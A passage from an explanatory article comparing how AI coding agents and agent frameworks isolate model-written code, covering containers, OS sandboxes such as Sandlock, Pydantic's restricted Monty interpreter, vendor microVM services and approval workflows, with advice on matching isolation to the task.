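Hosted platforms can make the choice for their customers. InfoQ's *Azure Logic Apps Adds Sandboxed Code Interpreters to Agent Workflows* (2026) reports that Azure Logic Apps, Microsoft's service for automating business tasks, runs agents' code in sandboxes isolated by Hyper-V, the company's virtual machine software. LangChain is retiring its own components for running code.

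### What developers turn on

A framework's list of sandboxes doesn't reveal how many applications use them. The closest evidence comes from studies of coding agents, which write and run software on a developer's behalf. *Harness Engineering* (2026) examined the source code of 11 such agents and lists these forms of isolation:

| Isolation | Coding agents |
|---|---|
| Containers or a choice of environments | OpenHands, mini-swe-agent, Hermes |
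| Operating-system sandbox | Codex, Gemini CLI |
| Optional sandbox | Claude Code |
| Optional separate copy of the project | Mistral Vibe |
| None | Aider, Pi, OpenCode, OpenClaw |

Four of the 11 have no sandbox. Mistral Vibe's separate copy protects the original project from mistakes but doesn't stop a program from reading the user's other files. Pi's developers deliberately left out a sandbox, and OpenCode relies on rules about which commands need permission.

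Studying an agent's source code can't establish which environment people run it in. *Harness Engineering* lists Docker for mini-swe-agent, but *Inside the Scaffold* (2026) classifies the same agent as running commands in ordinary subprocesses, without a container. Both descriptions can be correct if the agent supports several environments, in which case its security depends on which one the user selects. *Inside the Scaffold* found no standard approach across the agents it studied.

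Coding agents are also a poor guide to the applications developers build with frameworks. The agents often need to change real files and run whole test suites, whereas an invoice assistant may call only two functions. The public web applications that Liu and colleagues tested are a closer match, and few of them protected the server, but developers were building more hastily at the time.

Modal, a sandbox service, reports that its customer Lovable, whose product builds apps from plain-language requests, ran more than a million sandboxes in 48 hours at its peak. This shows that isolation is practical on a large scale, but the figure does not measure what share of developers use it.

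### The dispute over full sandboxes

Pydantic argued in the title of its launch article that "you probably don't need a full sandbox". Many agents only call functions and combine the results, so Pydantic sees little point in giving them a complete computer and then restricting it with different tools on each operating system. On the podcast Talk Python, Pydantic's chief executive, Samuel Colvin, said that Monty only has to run the code models write, not replace CPython for existing applications. He was surprised by how rarely models need classes.

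Colvin also said Pydantic hadn't built on Starlark because Starlark's designers chose its features on principle, while Pydantic wants to add whatever features models try to use. Adding these features should mean fewer failed scripts, but each one adds code that could contain a security flaw.

Critics would rather keep standard Python and have the operating system confine it. Wang and Zheng's Sandlock takes this approach. It first removes the program's access to most files and network connections, using Linux kernel features that need no administrator rights. A supervisor process then handles decisions that depend on what the program does, such as which website it tries to contact. Ordinary Python, including packages with compiled parts, ran under Sandlock without changes, and Sandlock added only about 5 ms to start-up time.

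On Linux, then, start-up time is a weak reason to prefer Monty to CPython for an agent that waits seconds for each model reply. Pydantic's complaint about removing access piece by piece applies to how Sandlock handles system calls, but not files. Sandlock blocks a list of dangerous system calls and lets the others through to the kernel, while it denies access to files unless the developer grants it.

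Sandlock needs Linux 6.12 or later, and Wang and Zheng assume that the kernel has no exploitable flaws. They tested Sandlock's restrictions with only ten checks, all of which it passed. They recommend a microVM instead for hostile code from many customers on one server.

Sandbox vendors emphasise what a full environment can do. In its guide to seven services, Modal ranks its own first. It supports any programming language and offers a wide choice of graphics processors, which are useful for training a model but not for simple tasks such as adding up invoices. These benefits are real, though Modal has a commercial interest in promoting them. Pydantic has a commercial interest too, since it sells a hosted version of Monty.

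Modal isolates code with gVisor, while E2B uses Firecracker microVMs. *AI Code Sandboxes* (2026) compares such products by their exposure to attack, their past flaws and how quickly they receive fixes. These criteria are better grounds for choosing a service than its start-up time, but Modal's guide leaves out past flaws and the speed of fixes.

Pydantic's argument is convincing for agents that mainly call functions, provided that Monty's interpreter, which is still new, runs inside a second barrier when the data is valuable. The argument is much weaker for agents that analyse data, because wrapping each package by hand soon becomes more work than setting up a container.

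### Matching a design to the task

If the finance team wants the same overdue total every Monday, the developer can write the calculation and the email in ordinary code and may not need a model. If users can ask for the total in their own words, a structured call to one narrow function is enough. Microsoft recommends direct tool calls for tasks that need only one or two of them, because model-written code saves little in those cases.

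A restricted language is usually the best choice for calculations that the developer can't predict. It is also fast. In *EffGen* (2026), a calculator that accepted only approved operations typically took 0.07 ms, compared with 28.1 ms for starting Python in a sandboxed subprocess and running a trivial program. CEL is a good choice when the calculation also involves selecting records.

An agent that chains many tools together benefits most from code actions, and Monty or Hyperlight can run them without giving the script access to anything besides those tools. In Microsoft's framework, a person approves or rejects each program as a whole, and if any available tool requires approval, every program does, even one that never calls that tool. Microsoft therefore suggests keeping actions such as sending email outside the program, as structured calls with their own approval. For the invoice task,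 the script would return 2,000, and the model would then request the email separately. This adds a model call, but the bookkeeper sees the recipient before anything is sent. Monty can instead pause the script at the email call, which avoids the extra model call.

Data-tracking policies like CaMeL's are another reason to keep some tool calls outside the generated program. The November release of Microsoft's *agent-framework-hyperlight* (2026) comes with a warning that FIDES, a system that labels data and enforces policies, can't check tool calls made inside generated code. A developer who relies on those policies has to call tools directly for now.

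Open-ended data analysis usually needs a container or a microVM, because nobody can list in advance every package and method an analyst might want. Pyodide is a reasonable alternative if it has the necessary packages and the developer confines its JavaScript host.
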